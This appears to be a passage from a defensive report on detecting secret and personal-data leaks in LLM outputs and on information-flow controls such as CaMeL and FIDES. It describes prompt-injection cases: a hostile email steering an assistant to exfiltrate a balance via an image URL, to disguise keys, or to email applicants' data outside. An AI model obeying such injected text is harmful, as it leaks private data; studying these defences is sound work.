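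*AgentLeak* (2026) tested systems in which several agents work together. Private data appeared in 27.2% of final outputs and 68.8% of messages between agents. The total across all measured channels was 68.9%, so a scanner that checked only the final output would have missed about three in five of the leaks. The study used older models such as GPT-4o, but any application that scans only the chat window has the same gap.

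### Formats, checksums and randomness

A detector's recall is the share of real secrets it finds, and its precision is the share of its alarms that are right.

The simplest detectors search for patterns. Many companies start their access keys with a fixed prefix, which makes the keys easy to find. A password that somebody made up has no prefix, so a pattern can find it only from nearby words such as "password:".

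Small details of a scanner's patterns affect which secrets it finds. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (2026) ran three scanners on the same 400 keys in known formats and measured recall of 100%, 80% and 60%. Gitleaks missed keys followed by any of eight characters that commonly come after a key in source code. TruffleHog missed every Amazon key that appeared alone but found all of them when a secret access key accompanied them. A developer who uses such a scanner on chat replies should test it with keys in ordinary sentences, where a full stop or Markdown may follow the key.

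Card numbers contain a checksum, a digit calculated from the others. To check a number, a program doubles every second digit from the right, subtracts 9 from any result above 9, and adds everything up. The total must be a multiple of 10. For the test number 4111 1111 1111 1111, the total is 30, so the number passes. About one random number in ten also passes, so the check removes roughly 90% of the false alarms from invoice and tracking numbers.

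*Broad and Efficient PII Detection with Unified Labels* (Hsu and Berlin, 2026) gives examples of numbers that the checksum misclassifies. An order number can happen to be 4111 1111 1111 1111, which passes the check. A customer may also write "my credit card number is" before a mistyped number, which fails the check but still reveals most of the card number.

Randomness tests look for keys with no known format. They usually measure entropy, −Σ *p* log₂ *p*, where *p* is each distinct character's share of the string. A long random key has high entropy, but so do file hashes and random record identifiers. Passwords that people choose often have low entropy. For example, `Summer2026!` and the word "outstanding" have the same entropy, about 3.1 bits per character, because each has eleven characters, two of which occur twice.

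### Names, addresses and other personal data

No pattern describes all human names. A named-entity model instead uses the surrounding words to label names, addresses, phone numbers and so on. OpenAI's Privacy Filter labels eight categories, including credentials. Its weights are downloadable and it is small enough to run on a laptop, so a company can scan replies without sending them to anyone else.

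These models depend heavily on context. *Model Card for OpenAI Privacy Filter* (de Bourcy, Ghalebikesabi and colleagues, 2026) reports that in tests the filter found 91.9% of phone numbers when a phrase such as "my home landline number" came before the number, 57.4% when the phrase came after it, and 31.8% when there was no phrase.

Names are harder to detect than data in fixed formats. Uppala (2026), in *OpenAI Privacy Filter*, tested the filter on 32 datasets. It did best on email addresses and phone numbers and worst on people's names and postal addresses. In *Mind the Gap* (2026), the open-source tool Presidio found every American social security number and every IP address, while a general language model missed 22.3% of names in unfamiliar text. Combining methods therefore makes sense. *GLiNER Guard* (2026) describes a pipeline that uses rules for emails, access tokens and bank cards,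 and a model for other entities.

Presidio's perfect score doesn't carry over to other data, though. In *PIIBench* (2026), it missed all 23 card numbers, possibly because the invented numbers in the test data failed its checksum test. In *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring* (2026), which tested it on transcripts of maths lessons, Presidio found about three quarters of the personal data, but three quarters of its alarms were false because it mistook mathematical notation for identifiers. An assistant that often discusses invoices would probably cause similar mistakes.

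### Known secrets and planted strings

A company can search a model's replies for its own access keys. This finds every exact copy, and a long random key will practically never match by accident. It misses keys the company didn't search for, such as a supplier's, and any copy with a single character changed. The method doesn't suit short secrets, because a four-digit door code will also match years and invoice amounts.

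The list of keys would be valuable to a thief, so the scanner can instead store a keyed hash of each key, a short code that nobody can compute or check without a separate secret. To find a key in a reply, the scanner must hash every stretch of text as long as the key. A 3,000-character reply has 2,961 stretches of 40 characters, which a computer can hash very quickly.

A canary string is a meaningless, unique string that a developer plants in text that should stay hidden, such as the system prompt. If the string appears in a reply, the model has copied some of that text. Using a different string in each confidential document shows which one leaked. The method has almost no false alarms, but it misses summaries and partial quotations that leave out the string.

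A planted string can also look like a working access key. If the company sets an alert for any attempt to log in with the fake key, it can learn of a leak that every scanner missed.

### A second model as judge

A second language model can check whether a reply reveals something it shouldn't. It is the only one of these detectors that might flag the sentence about the Leeds office as confidential, provided its instructions explain what the company considers secret.

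Ahrend and colleagues compared judges with simpler detectors on the output of their six models. Claude Opus had the highest recall, at 84.8%, against 56.0% for an entity model called GLiNER2 and 41.4% for patterns. The patterns were crude (one treated an "@" as a sign of an email address), so better ones might have done well. GLiNER2 did best on a score that gave card and social security numbers nine times the weight of names. Opus's results on that score, where 1 is perfect, also varied widely with the model it was checking. It got over 0.99 for replies from Llama and Mixtral but 0.256 for those from DeepSeek-R1.

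A judge can itself leak data. During development, the researchers found that the judge tended to give long answers that could repeat the data, so they restricted it to a fixed output format. Like any model that reads outside text, the judge is also open to prompt injection.

People still find secrets that models overlook. *Secrets That Survive Everything* (2026) built a benchmark from the published code of 113 business applications using both a model and a manual search, and the manual search found credentials the model had missed.

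### What the benchmarks measure

The table gives precision and recall on several kinds of text. De Bourcy and colleagues calculated them by counting tokens, while Uppala counted a detection as correct only if it covered exactly the right characters.

| Detector | Text | Source | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Privacy Filter | Credentials in program code | De Bourcy and colleagues | 74.7% | 96.5% |
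| Privacy Filter | Invented personal data | Uppala | 86.2% | 84.9% |
| Privacy Filter | Customer support | Uppala | 46.2% | 84.1% |
| Privacy Filter | Financial documents | Uppala | 63.8% | 49.0% |
| Privacy Filter | Medical questions | Uppala | 32.4% | 81.8% |
| Presidio | Maths lessons | *Utility-Preserving De-Identification for Math Tutoring* | 25.4% | 74.7% |

Some of the apparent errors are disagreements about what counts as personal data. The medical dataset labels only details of the person asking the question, so flagging someone else's name counts as a false alarm. De Bourcy and colleagues raised precision and recall to about 96% by training the filter on a tenth of a similar dataset's examples, and a company with its own definition of personal data could reasonably do the same.

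Hsu and Berlin show how much a detector's measured recall can depend on the labels. In one dataset, the code in "Don't forget to bring your YV9022888!" was originally labelled as a passport number, although the sentence doesn't mention a passport. They had a model relabel the data under stricter written rules. For the same output, their detector's recall for driving licence numbers was 30.6% with the old labels and 90.9% with the new ones.

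They also set each detector to wrongly flag at most 0.1% of 100,000 real chatbot conversations for any one category. Their own detector then caught 97.6% of card numbers, compared with 68.5% for one from NVIDIA and 56.8% for one from Fastino. Allowing a false-flag rate of 0.5% raised Fastino's result to 81.5%. Training on labels made under the same rules gave their detector an advantage, but it also led most comparisons under the original labels.

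### Why most alarms can be false

Even a detector with a low false-positive rate can produce mostly false alarms if secrets are rare. Suppose an application sends a million responses, of which 100 contain a secret. A detector that catches 95% of those 100 and wrongly flags 0.5% of the other responses would raise 95 correct alarms and about 5,000 false ones.

| | Responses | Flagged |
|---|---|---|
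| Contain a secret | 100 | 95 |
| Contain no secret | 999,900 | about 5,000 |
| Total | 1,000,000 | about 5,095 |

Only 95 of the 5,095 alarms are right, which is under 2%. A person who spent a minute on each alarm would need about 85 hours to check them all. In general, a detector's precision is *rb* / (*rb* + *f*(1 − *b*)), where *b* is the share of responses that contain a secret, *r* is the detector's recall and *f* is the share of the other responses that it wrongly flags. For half of the alarms to be right, the detector could wrongly flag only about one harmless response in 10,500.

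The same detector would be much more precise for a more common type of data. According to Hsu and Berlin's labels, 0.41% of the real conversations contained a phone number. At that frequency, with the same recall and false alarm rate, 44% of the alarms would be correct. Precision on a benchmark full of secrets is therefore a poor guide to precision on ordinary traffic.

False positives also add up across categories. If a detector looks for twelve kinds of data and wrongly flags 0.1% of responses for each, it could wrongly flag up to 1.2% of responses in total.

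A second check on the flagged responses makes the alarms much more reliable. If it dismisses 99% of the false alarms and keeps 90% of the real ones, about 50 false and 86 real alarms remain, so 63% of the remaining alarms are real. However, the system misses nine more secrets. Hsu and Berlin designed their small detector for the first stage of such a system, so that slower methods examine only a few responses.

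Scanners also need to distinguish real keys from placeholders such as `insert_your_key`. *WildCode Revisited* (2025) found 1,380 programming conversations in which users' prompts contained something that resembled a key, and used a classifier to separate real keys from placeholders. Of 209 conversations inspected by hand, 111 contained real keys.

### Text that leaves before the scan is complete

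When a reply is streamed, the first half of a key can appear on screen before a scanner has seen the second half. Deleting the text afterwards doesn't help if the reader has already copied it or if, as in SearchLeak, the browser has already sent it out in an image URL.

For fixed formats, the server can hold back the latest part of the reply. If the longest key has 100 characters, a delay of 100 characters is enough, and most users won't notice it. An entity model needs more text because the phrase that identifies a number may come after it. Each layer of OpenAI's filter takes in up to 128 tokens on either side. At 50 tokens per second, waiting for 128 more tokens would take about two and a half seconds. A judge that assesses the whole reply can't start until the model finishes.

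### Secrets in another form

A hostile email can contain instructions for the model to put spaces between a key's characters, spell out its digits or convert it to another encoding. De Bourcy and colleagues tested a filter on the first two methods, but not against an attacker who adapted to it. Recall was 63.1% for text with unusual spacing and 67.4% for digits written as words. *REDACT* (2026) found that Presidio caught only 7% of disguised personal details.

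The scanner can remove spaces and invisible characters and undo common encodings before it searches. This catches simple disguises, but an attacker can invent a new code and explain it to the model in a sentence. The model can also reveal a secret without writing it, through its answers to a series of yes-or-no questions or through its choice of links.

Scanning is therefore much better at catching accidents than attacks. A model that copies a password from an old document usually copies it exactly.

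### Legitimate names and numbers

If an employee asks the assistant who handles the company's account at the paper supplier, the correct answer is a name and a phone number. A scanner that removes all personal data would block this answer, while one that allows all names would also let through the names of people on sick leave.

Detectors differ on which phone numbers to flag. OpenAI's filter tries to flag only private ones, whereas Hsu and Berlin's also flags a company's switchboard and leaves the application to decide what to do with it. That decision depends on who is asking, because the same text stating a salary is a proper answer for the payroll clerk and a leak for anyone else.

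### Blocking, redacting and logging

Blocking withholds the whole reply. It suits access keys, which an assistant almost never needs to show anyone, but with the detector in the example it would also withhold about 5,000 harmless replies.

Redaction replaces only the sensitive part, for instance with `<PRIVATE_PHONE>`, so a false alarm removes only a few words. It can leave part of a secret in the text, because a detector may find a key but misjudge where it starts or ends. It is also the wrong choice for a tool call. A payment request with a label in place of the account number is at best invalid, so the application should stop it and report the reason.

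Blocking and redaction can both confirm a guess. Suppose the scanner blocks any reply that contains the company's four-digit door code. Someone who gets the model to list half of the possible codes can tell which half contains the right one by whether the reply is blocked, and can find the code in 14 replies by repeatedly halving the list. If the scanner redacts the code instead, one list of all the codes is enough, because the right one will be missing. This is another reason not to put short secrets on an exact-match list.

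Logging an alarm while letting the reply through doesn't stop the leak, but it lets a company measure false alarms before it starts blocking replies. The log then holds the sensitive data, often where more people can read it than could read the original document. Ahrend and colleagues count anyone who later gains access to stored transcripts or logs as a possible attacker. The Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre advises recording who asked, which sources the model used and what it returned, while protecting the log so that it doesn't become a new leak. The alarm itself needs only the type of data, its position and a keyed hash of the value, which shows whether the same value has leaked before. Any full transcript needs redaction or its own strict access limits.

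### Keeping the data away from the model

A model can't reveal a password it never receives. The office assistant needs to query the database, but the tool that sends the query can hold the password and return only the rows to the model. Invicti quotes the 2026 edition of OWASP's list: "any contents of the context should not be considered a secret". The context is everything the model reads.

If the model needs a person's details only as a reference, the application can replace them with stand-ins and restore them in the response. *SurrogateShield* (2026) did this for 1,124 queries, and none of the personal data identified in them reached the model. The application should restore the details only in text that the user will read. If it also restored them in links and image addresses, it would leak them to an attacker who controlled those addresses.

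For documents, the most important control is to search with the employee's own permissions. When a warehouse worker asks about salaries, the search returns no salary files, however the worker words the question. This control doesn't depend on detecting salary data, and the payroll clerk still gets an answer. The search has to apply the permissions before it selects documents. HackerDNA notes that many systems search the whole index before checking permissions, so the number of results or the response time can reveal that other people's documents exist.

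Permission checks depend on the permissions being set correctly, and shared drives often let far too many people read a file. An employee may also be allowed to open an old project document that contains a password. Scanning documents before indexing them would catch some of these passwords once, instead of in every reply. Scanning the output is still useful for catching the rest, and for catching data the model memorised in training, which permission checks don't cover.

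Permission checks at retrieval also don't control where the data goes next. The accounts clerk is allowed to read every supplier's prices. If one supplier's email led the assistant to quote a competitor's prices in a draft reply, every search would have been permitted, and the prices would look like any others. Stopping that draft requires a rule based on where the prices came from and who will receive them.

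## Tracking untrusted data through the application

To keep one supplier's prices out of a reply to another, an application has to record where each piece of text came from, even after a model has rewritten it. Programmers call this taint tracking, or information flow control when it also records who may read the text.

### Labels before language models

*A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) gave the idea a mathematical form. Every value has a label, a relation → specifies which labels may flow into which, and an operator ⊕ combines labels. If a program computes a value from inputs labelled *A*₁, …, *A*ₙ, it may store the result in a place labelled *B* only if *A*₁ ⊕ … ⊕ *A*ₙ → *B*. In a system with medical, financial and criminal records, for example, a result based on medical and financial data may go only to places cleared for both. The labels form a lattice, so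 any two labels have a least strict label that covers both, and a program can always work out the label of a combined result.

The programming language Perl has a simpler version called taint mode, which its documentation strongly recommends for server programs. Perl marks command-line arguments, environment variables and the contents of files as tainted. If tainted data reaches a shell command or an operation that changes files, the program stops with an error. The programmer can clear the mark by matching the data against a pattern and using the part that matched. Perl doesn't check whether the pattern is sensible, so a pattern that accepts any character clears the mark from any data.

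Carnegie Mellon University's Software Engineering Institute (SEI) describes Perl's taint mode as a simple model for detecting flaws such as SQL injection. For a web application, the tainted data is whatever a visitor sends, and the database query is the sink. Perl checks only some sinks, and printing isn't one of them, so a program in taint mode can still print a visitor's script into a web page.

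All these systems have the same five parts.

| Term | Meaning | In the office assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Source | Where data enters the application | The mailbox or the invoice database |
| Label | A mark recording the data's integrity (whether to trust it) and confidentiality (who may read it) | Untrusted, readable by the clerk and the supplier |
| Propagation | The rule for labelling results | A summary gets the combined labels of everything it is based on |
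| Sink rule | The condition that data must meet before a sink acts on it | Nobody may receive text they aren't allowed to read |
| Declassification | A deliberate decision to relax a label | The clerk approves sending a figure to the supplier |

### From an email to an image address

Labels would stop the office assistant from carrying out the emailed request to put the company's unpaid balance in the URL of the supplier's logo. The application labels the email body as untrusted and private, and only the clerk and the supplier may read it. The balance is labeled as trusted because it comes from the company's database, and the clerk and the finance director may read it.

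The assistant writes a summary based on both sources. One untrusted source is enough to make the summary untrusted. Only people allowed to read both sources may read the summary, so its permitted readers are {clerk, supplier} ∩ {clerk, finance director} = {clerk}. The image address inherits the same labels.

Before the browser displays the image, the application checks who would receive the address. Loading the image would send it to the supplier's server, and the supplier isn't a permitted reader, so the application refuses to load the image. It can still show the summary to the clerk. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* suggests treating links to any host that isn't on an allow-list as public channels, which would also block the image.

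This check doesn't depend on recognising the email as an attack. It would also catch the draft reply containing a competitor's prices, because only the clerk may read both the paper supplier's email and the competitor's price list.

### Label creep

In ordinary code, a program can track which inputs a result depends on. If it adds two invoices, the total gets the labels of those two invoices and no others. A language model's output could depend on anything in its context, so the cautious approach is to give every output the labels of everything in the context.

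These labels only become stricter. If the clerk reads the supplier's email and then asks the assistant to send an unrelated report to the finance director, the application refuses, because the finance director is not allowed to read the email. This is label creep, in which restrictions spread until they block harmless work. If one in ten of the items an assistant reads is untrusted, and they arrive independently, the chance that its context is still trusted after *n* items is 0.9ⁿ, which is 35% after ten items and 12% after 20.

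*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) measured the drop in task completion on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments. With GPT-4o, an ordinary agent completed 98.8% of the banking tasks. When the researchers labelled the whole conversation and blocked actions that broke their rules, it completed 37.5%, even though there were no attacks.

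A company can slow label creep by dividing the work among several agents, so that the one reading emails doesn't also send reports. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated this without real models. Labels spread furthest when agents had to pass information through intermediaries, such as a central coordinator. They spread least when every agent was directly connected to every other, but that means monitoring 10 connections for five agents and 190 for 20. Giving the sensitive tools to only a few agents also helped. None of these designs fully prevented label creep, so Gregory and colleagues conclude that systems also need ways to declassify data.

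Another approach is to estimate which inputs the model actually used. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) does this from the model's attention, the weights that determine how much it draws on each earlier token. On AgentDojo, the tool removed 50% of the unnecessary labels and missed 3.9% of the real dependencies. A rule against acting on untrusted data blocked all 34 attack calls in the test. However, the tool's limit on misses holds only if new cases resemble those used to calibrate it, and an attacker who writes emails to fool the tool would break that assumption.

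Even a perfect estimate would leave many outputs restricted, because most inputs affect the output. In Xu and colleagues' sample of open-source programs, only 12% to 14% of the inputs to a model had no effect on its answer.

### CaMeL

A more thorough solution is to keep untrusted text away from the model that decides what to do. In 2023, Simon Willison proposed doing this with two models. A privileged model has tools but never reads untrusted text, and a quarantined model reads the text but has no tools. The privileged model refers to the quarantined model's answers by name, such as `$email-summary-1`, without seeing them.

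Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, describes a flaw that Google DeepMind researchers found in this design. If a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes, hostile text in the notes can make the quarantined model return an attacker's address instead. The privileged model then follows the correct plan but sends the document to the attacker.

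Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues at DeepMind published CaMeL in 2025 to fix this. It works in five steps:

1. A planning model reads the user's request and the descriptions of the tools, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools.
3. If the program needs information from untrusted text, it asks a quarantined model, whose answer goes into a variable that the planning model can't see.
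4. The interpreter records where each variable's contents came from and who may read them.
5. Before each tool call, a policy written in ordinary code checks these records and allows or refuses the call.

If the clerk asks the office assistant to pay the invoice in the supplier's latest email, the planning model might write this simplified program:

```
email = get_latest_email("paper supplier")
amount = ask_quarantined("What is the amount due?", email)
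account = ask_quarantined("Which account is it for?", email)
make_payment(account, amount)
```

The account number may be valid, but the interpreter has recorded that it came from the email. If the company's policy allows only account numbers from its own supplier records, the interpreter blocks the payment. A better program would look up the account in those records and ask the clerk to confirm the amount.

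CaMeL's guarantee concerns the agent's actions. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) states that untrusted data can influence which of the plan's existing branches the program takes, but can't add new ones. A hostile email can therefore change `amount`, but it can't make the assistant forward the mailbox if the plan has no such step, even if the email completely fools the quarantined model. CaMeL relies on its policies to prevent misuse of the planned steps.

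The guarantee holds only if the user's request and the tool descriptions are trustworthy. If the clerk pastes the supplier's email into the request, the planning model treats it as an instruction. The interpreter must also have no relevant bugs. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) warns that Python's exceptions and flexible types make it hard to prove in advance how information will flow through a program.

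### CaMeL on AgentDojo

Willison quotes the DeepMind researchers as writing that CaMeL "effectively solves the AgentDojo benchmark". *AgentSys* (2026), *SecureClaw* (2026) and *Kairos* (2026) later reran CaMeL on AgentDojo to compare it with their own systems. *Kairos* reports results for three models.

| Test of CaMeL | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without attacks | Tasks completed under attack |
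|---|---|---|---|
| *AgentSys*, GPT-4o-mini | 0% | 30.0% | 33.4% |
| *SecureClaw* | 0% | 29.9% | 31.0% |
| *Kairos*, first model | 0.2% | 38.0% | 40.7% |
| *Kairos*, second model | 0.4% | 40.4% | 37.0% |
| *Kairos*, third model | 0% | 26.5% | 26.0% |

These results support the security claim but also show that the defense leaves many tasks unfinished. Completion rates are sometimes higher under attack, but this doesn't mean that attacks help, because the attacked tests repeat each task with several attacks and so give some tasks more weight.

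The comparisons may be somewhat unfair to CaMeL, because researchers have less reason to tune a rival system, and *SecureClaw* had to adapt the published code. The results also depend heavily on how well the planning model writes programs. But they are consistent enough to suggest that a company using CaMeL with a similar model would complete far fewer tasks. The *AgentSys* system completed 64.4% of tasks when there were no attacks and let 0.78% of attacks succeed, so accepting a small risk can more than double the number of tasks completed.

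CaMeL also needs extra model calls to read untrusted text. If a policy blocks a program's last step, the calls made before it are wasted. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) reduces this waste by checking the program before it runs. It converts the program into a diagram of all its possible paths, and a standard verification tool checks every path against rules such as "no payment may have an untrusted recipient". If a path breaks a rule, the planning model receives that path and tries to repair the program. The check simplifies loops, so it can reject safe programs.

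### FIDES

CaMeL's planning model writes the whole program before it receives any results. FIDES, which Costa and colleagues developed at Microsoft, keeps the usual agent loop, in which a model chooses one action, receives the result and then chooses the next.

FIDES keeps a label for the conversation. If a tool returns something with a stricter label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. For an email, the model might see the trusted fields and a name such as `#read_emails_0.subject` in place of the subject line. The conversation stays trusted, and the model can still pass the hidden text to another tool.

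The main model can use text hidden in a variable in two ways. It can open the variable, which adds the text and its label to the conversation and may block later actions. It can also ask a quarantined model a question about the text, and the answer goes into another variable. For example, to send a colleague a summary of three emails, the main model asks the quarantined model for the summary and sends the resulting variable without reading it.

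A separate policy engine checks each tool call before it runs. One of its rules allows important actions only if no untrusted data influenced the decision to take them. Another allows a call to send data out only if every recipient has permission to read it. FIDES can apply different rules to different arguments of a call, for example by requiring a trusted recipient but allowing an untrusted message.

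The confidentiality guarantee covers direct data flows, such as copying a balance into an email. It assumes that the labels and policies are correct and, like CaMeL's, that the user's messages and the tool descriptions are trustworthy.

Without policy checks, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. The 21 succeeded because FIDES's model could still open variables containing attacks. With the checks on, no attacks succeeded against either agent. AgentDojo's automatic scoring counted three successes against FIDES, but Costa and colleagues inspected them and judged them harmless or wrongly scored. The table shows the percentage of tasks GPT-4o completed when there were no attacks.

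| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no checks | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

With the checks on, FIDES completed an average of 50% of tasks across the four environments, compared with 42% for the ordinary agent. Without the checks, the ordinary agent completed 84%. Hiding text therefore recovers some of the tasks lost to label creep, but far from all of them. FIDES's result on the office tasks may be slightly inflated, because the researchers used those tasks to refine its instructions.

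Some of the failures came from GPT-4o confusing variable names or calling tools it didn't need. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's lead over the ordinary agent grew from 8 to 16 percentage points. Newer models would probably narrow the gap further. FIDES also takes longer and uses more tokens, because each question to the quarantined model adds a step, and Costa and colleagues hadn't yet optimised these steps.

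Other systems have the same trade-off. In *SPA* (2026), an agent that plans its actions in advance completed 53% of AgentDojo tasks without information flow control and 29% with it. Four of 949 attacks succeeded without the control, and adding it stopped all four. An accounts department might accept the drop in completed tasks to protect its payment system, but the drop would be hard to justify for an assistant that only drafts text.

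### Early use in products

Microsoft announced in *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) that FIDES was available to developers as an experimental feature of its Agent Framework. By default, the framework hides untrusted results from the main model. A developer can turn this off and rely on the policy checks alone, which avoids a second model call but lets the main model read hostile text.

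Microsoft also worked with GitHub on experimental support for this kind of tracking in Copilot CLI, a coding agent for the terminal. GitHub's server for connecting agents to its service can now label the files and issues it returns. An agent that has read both untrusted and private content is not allowed to post publicly, which could stop a hostile issue in a public project from making the agent publish text from a private one. At launch, Copilot CLI enforced policies for only some of that server's tools and for no tools from other servers.

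### When labels are wrong or missing

The AgentDojo results for FIDES depend on unusually accurate labels. Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A company doesn't have a list of future attacks, so it has to work out who can write to each field.

In Microsoft's framework, data from an unlabeled tool counts as trusted and public. A developer who forgets to label the mailbox tool gets no error, and the policies treat hostile emails as the company's own text. Microsoft has asked developers whether the default should be untrusted instead. An untrusted default would be safer because, as with an allow-list, someone would notice an omission.

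GitHub's server labels everything in a private project as trusted, so if an employee copies a customer's bug report into one, the customer's words are labeled trusted too. FIDES can infer an email's readers from its sender and recipients, but this list will be incomplete if a recipient has forwarded the email to others.

Labels also have to be kept when data is stored. Otherwise, a dashboard that later displays the summary of a supplier's email has no label to distinguish it from the company's own notes. The application should store the label with the summary or treat everything in that field as untrusted.

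Labels can also disappear between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each protected by CaMeL, and asked it to send a summary of job applications to a colleague on Slack. One agent read the applications from a database where the researchers had planted a hostile instruction. A coordinating agent put the resulting summary into a request to a messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as trusted, followed the planted instruction and also emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

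The office assistant has the same weakness if it passes its summaries to a payments agent as instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues' fix, multi-CaMeL, sends trusted instructions and untrusted data separately and keeps the data labeled. In their extended version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately, and 0% with multi-CaMeL. The small difference between the last two results suggests that few attacks in the benchmark target this weakness, but anyone who knows how the agents are connected could look for it.

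### What a branch reveals

A program can reveal a secret without copying it. Denning gives the example `if a = 0 then b := 0`. If *b* starts with a nonzero value, anyone who sees *b* afterwards can tell whether *a* was 0, even if the program never ran the assignment. Denning calls this an implicit flow.

Suppose the office assistant sends the paper supplier a payment date only if the company's bank balance is above €50,000. The message contains no bank data, but the supplier learns something about the balance by receiving it. The choice among permitted web addresses leaks information in the same way. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that FIDES doesn't prevent such leaks. To stop them all, it would have to block nearly every externally visible action after the agent had read anything private.

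*Ghost in the Agent* (2026) tested NeuroTaint, a tool that looks for data flows in records of agents' actions. It caught 37 of 40 cases in which data influenced an action only through a branch. However, it also reported a flow in all 14 control cases where several sources covered similar topics but no flow had occurred. These false positives make it more useful for investigating incidents than for blocking actions automatically.

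Attackers can also use branches to make an agent follow a planned step at the wrong time, which *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) calls branch steering. AgentDojo plans average 4.9 tool calls, and most of their branches don't depend on outside data. An agent that operates a computer by looking at the screen has to prepare for many more situations. The paper's plans for such agents averaged 41.1 tool calls and 39.7 branches, which gives an attacker many more choices to influence even though the plan itself is fixed.

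### Text that misleads within the rules

An email can cause harm without triggering any forbidden action, as the hidden instruction did when it kept a contract deadline out of a summary. In Costa and colleagues' example, an email makes the quarantined model return an empty summary, which the assistant sends to the right person as planned.

A policy can require trusted data for the message as well as for the recipient, but then the assistant can't summarise outside emails. It is more practical to show the clerk that the summary comes from untrusted emails and link to the originals. For a payment, the application can compare the amount with the company's own records, since a label can only mark the amount as needing a check.

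### Tasks that follow outside instructions

Sometimes the user wants the assistant to do what an outside text says. "Pay the bill in this file" and "complete the tasks in my to-do list" are reasonable requests, but the assistant can't plan its actions until it has read the file or list. Costa and colleagues found that the right actions depend on such data in 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks, 10% of its travel tasks and over 40% of its banking and Slack tasks. Many of the banking tasks that FIDES failed were of this kind, and the policy required it to block them. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) makes the same point about agents that need to follow external documentation.

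FIDES offers a compromise in which the quarantined model may answer only yes or no, or choose from a short list. Suppose the clerk asks the assistant to create a calendar entry if the supplier has requested a meeting. The quarantined model reads the email and answers yes or no. The main model sees this answer and decides whether to continue. If it does, the quarantined model puts the date and time into a variable, and the main model passes the variable to the calendar without reading its contents.

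FIDES records the type of each answer in its label, so a policy can accept a yes-or-no answer from an untrusted email and reject free text from the same email. A yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit, and a choice from eight options carries at most three. Neither can contain a new instruction if the application enforces the limit with a schema.

This limits the attacker's influence but doesn't make the answer true. A hostile email can get a "yes" when there was no meeting request, leaving the clerk with a false calendar entry. The damage is greater in the recruiter's system that scores CVs. If the quarantined model answers whether to approve a candidate, the candidate needs to control only that one bit for the attack to succeed completely. A policy should therefore consider what depends on the answer as well as its length. Costa and colleagues left this feature out of their AgentDojo tests,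 so their results don't show how much it would help.

### Who writes the policies

Somebody has to decide which sources to trust and what each tool may do. To connect a new server to Microsoft's experimental labelling gateway, a developer must describe the format of each tool's results, write a function that passes labels from its inputs to its results, and write or choose a policy. An office assistant with 40 tools would need 40 sets of these, and each set could become wrong when its tool changes. Microsoft suggests choosing safe defaults based on the descriptions some tools already provide, such as whether they only read data.

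Under many policies, the system asks the user whether to allow an action when the rules don't settle it. The DeepMind researchers list the resulting user fatigue among CaMeL's limitations. A useful approval request for a payment would state that the account number came from yesterday's email and differs from the one in the company's records. Microsoft's framework shows which tool and label caused the block, but the company describes the framework's approvals as still coarse.

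*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) gives some of these decisions to a second model. Ordinary code tracks which private records may have influenced a message. The second model then compares the message with those records and answers only SAFE or BLOCKED. This can release harmless messages that a strict rule would stop, but an attacker may be able to influence the second model, as with any model used as a judge.

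Microsoft's example policy for chat messages allows a message if no untrusted data influenced the decision to send it, or if everyone in the channel may already read its contents. Otherwise, the user must approve it. The first condition assumes that a disclosure is intentional if no outsider could have caused it. But a model can misread a trusted request and post a salary list to the wrong channel, and the policy would allow this. Checking the readers of every message would stop the mistake, although the user would then have to approve some intentional disclosures.
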